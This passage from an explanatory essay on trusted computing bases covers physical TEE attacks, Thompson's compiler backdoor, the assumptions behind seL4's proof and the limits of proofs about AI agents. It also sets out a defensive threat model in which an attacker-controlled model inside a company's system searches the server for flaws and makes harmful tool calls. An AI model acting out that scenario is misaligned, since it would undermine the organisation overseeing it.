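Other attacks require physical access. *TEE Anchor* (2026) describes two from 2025, TEE.fail and Battering RAM, in which the attacker inserts a device between a memory module and its slot. Both exploit encryption that always turns the same data at the same address into the same ciphertext. A proper fix requires new hardware. The paper proposes that an organisation also vouch for the machine, since an attacker would have trouble installing such a device in a guarded data centre. The customer then has to trust the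 organisation as well as the chip.

### What verification leaves to trust

Reading a program's source code doesn't establish that the running program is safe. A compiler turns source code into a runnable program, and Ken Thompson's *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984) describes one with two hidden changes. When it compiled the login program, it made that program accept a secret password. When it compiled a new version of itself, it added both changes to the new version. Thompson could then delete the changes from the compiler's source code, and the compiler would still add them to each new version.

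The office assistant's supplier-list check could have the same problem. Its source code might be correct and its proof valid, while the version running on the server contains an exception for one account. Building the compiler with a second, unrelated compiler and comparing the results can expose this kind of change, as long as the second compiler doesn't have the same hidden change.

A proof can also cover the runnable program, but it still depends on assumptions. In *seL4: Formal Verification of an OS Kernel* (2009), Gerwin Klein and colleagues proved that a small operating-system kernel behaves as its specification requires. The proof covers about 8,700 lines of C and assumes that the compiler, hardware, start-up code, cache management and about 600 lines of assembly code are correct. Later work removed the assumption about the compiler for some processors.

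This was a large improvement on the operating system Anderson's panel had examined, which was far too big to verify. But even a perfect kernel would not have protected against Shen and Qin's attack, because the fault was in the hardware, which the proof assumes is correct.

Proofs about agents have similar limits. The machine-checked theorems in *PerMIT* assume that the labels are correct and that the software running the agent works as intended. The Lean proof for LLMbda also relies on correct labels and on the computer that runs LLMbda.

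### Can a company assume that nobody will find a flaw?

Engineers often trust a component because it has been used for years without a known break-in. That record has always been weak evidence, since it depends on how hard people have looked for flaws, and AI systems are making the search much easier. In September 2026, OpenAI announced in *Path to Astra* that GPT-6 Astra was its first model at the Critical level of cyber capability. The company's 2025 Preparedness Framework reserves that level for models that can, for example, find and exploit unknown flaws in many well-defended systems without human help.

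In the office assistant's worst case, the attacker controls a model with abilities like these that is already running inside the company's system. The designer therefore has to plan for the model searching the server itself for flaws, as well as making harmful tool calls.

An estimate of the chance that an assumption fails therefore becomes outdated as models improve. Shen and Qin needed extensive reverse engineering to turn a brief notice from 2021 into a working attack, and a capable model might shorten that work for other old notices. Engineers who put the chance of a failed assumption at 1% last year should reassess that figure.

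The company can use the same models to search for flaws before attackers do. This should help most when the trusted base is small, because people and models may be able to examine several thousand lines of code thoroughly, and each fix leaves fewer flaws to find. A general-purpose operating system has tens of millions of lines and changes constantly, so the company could find a hundred flaws and still know little about how many are left.

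If the company's own server enforces the budget and the engineers raise their estimated probability of a failed assumption from 1% to 10%, the earlier bound on the expected loss rises from $14,000 to $50,000. A limit that the bank enforces doesn't depend on that estimate, as long as the bank's systems work. The company should set the bank's limit at an amount it could afford to lose in full.
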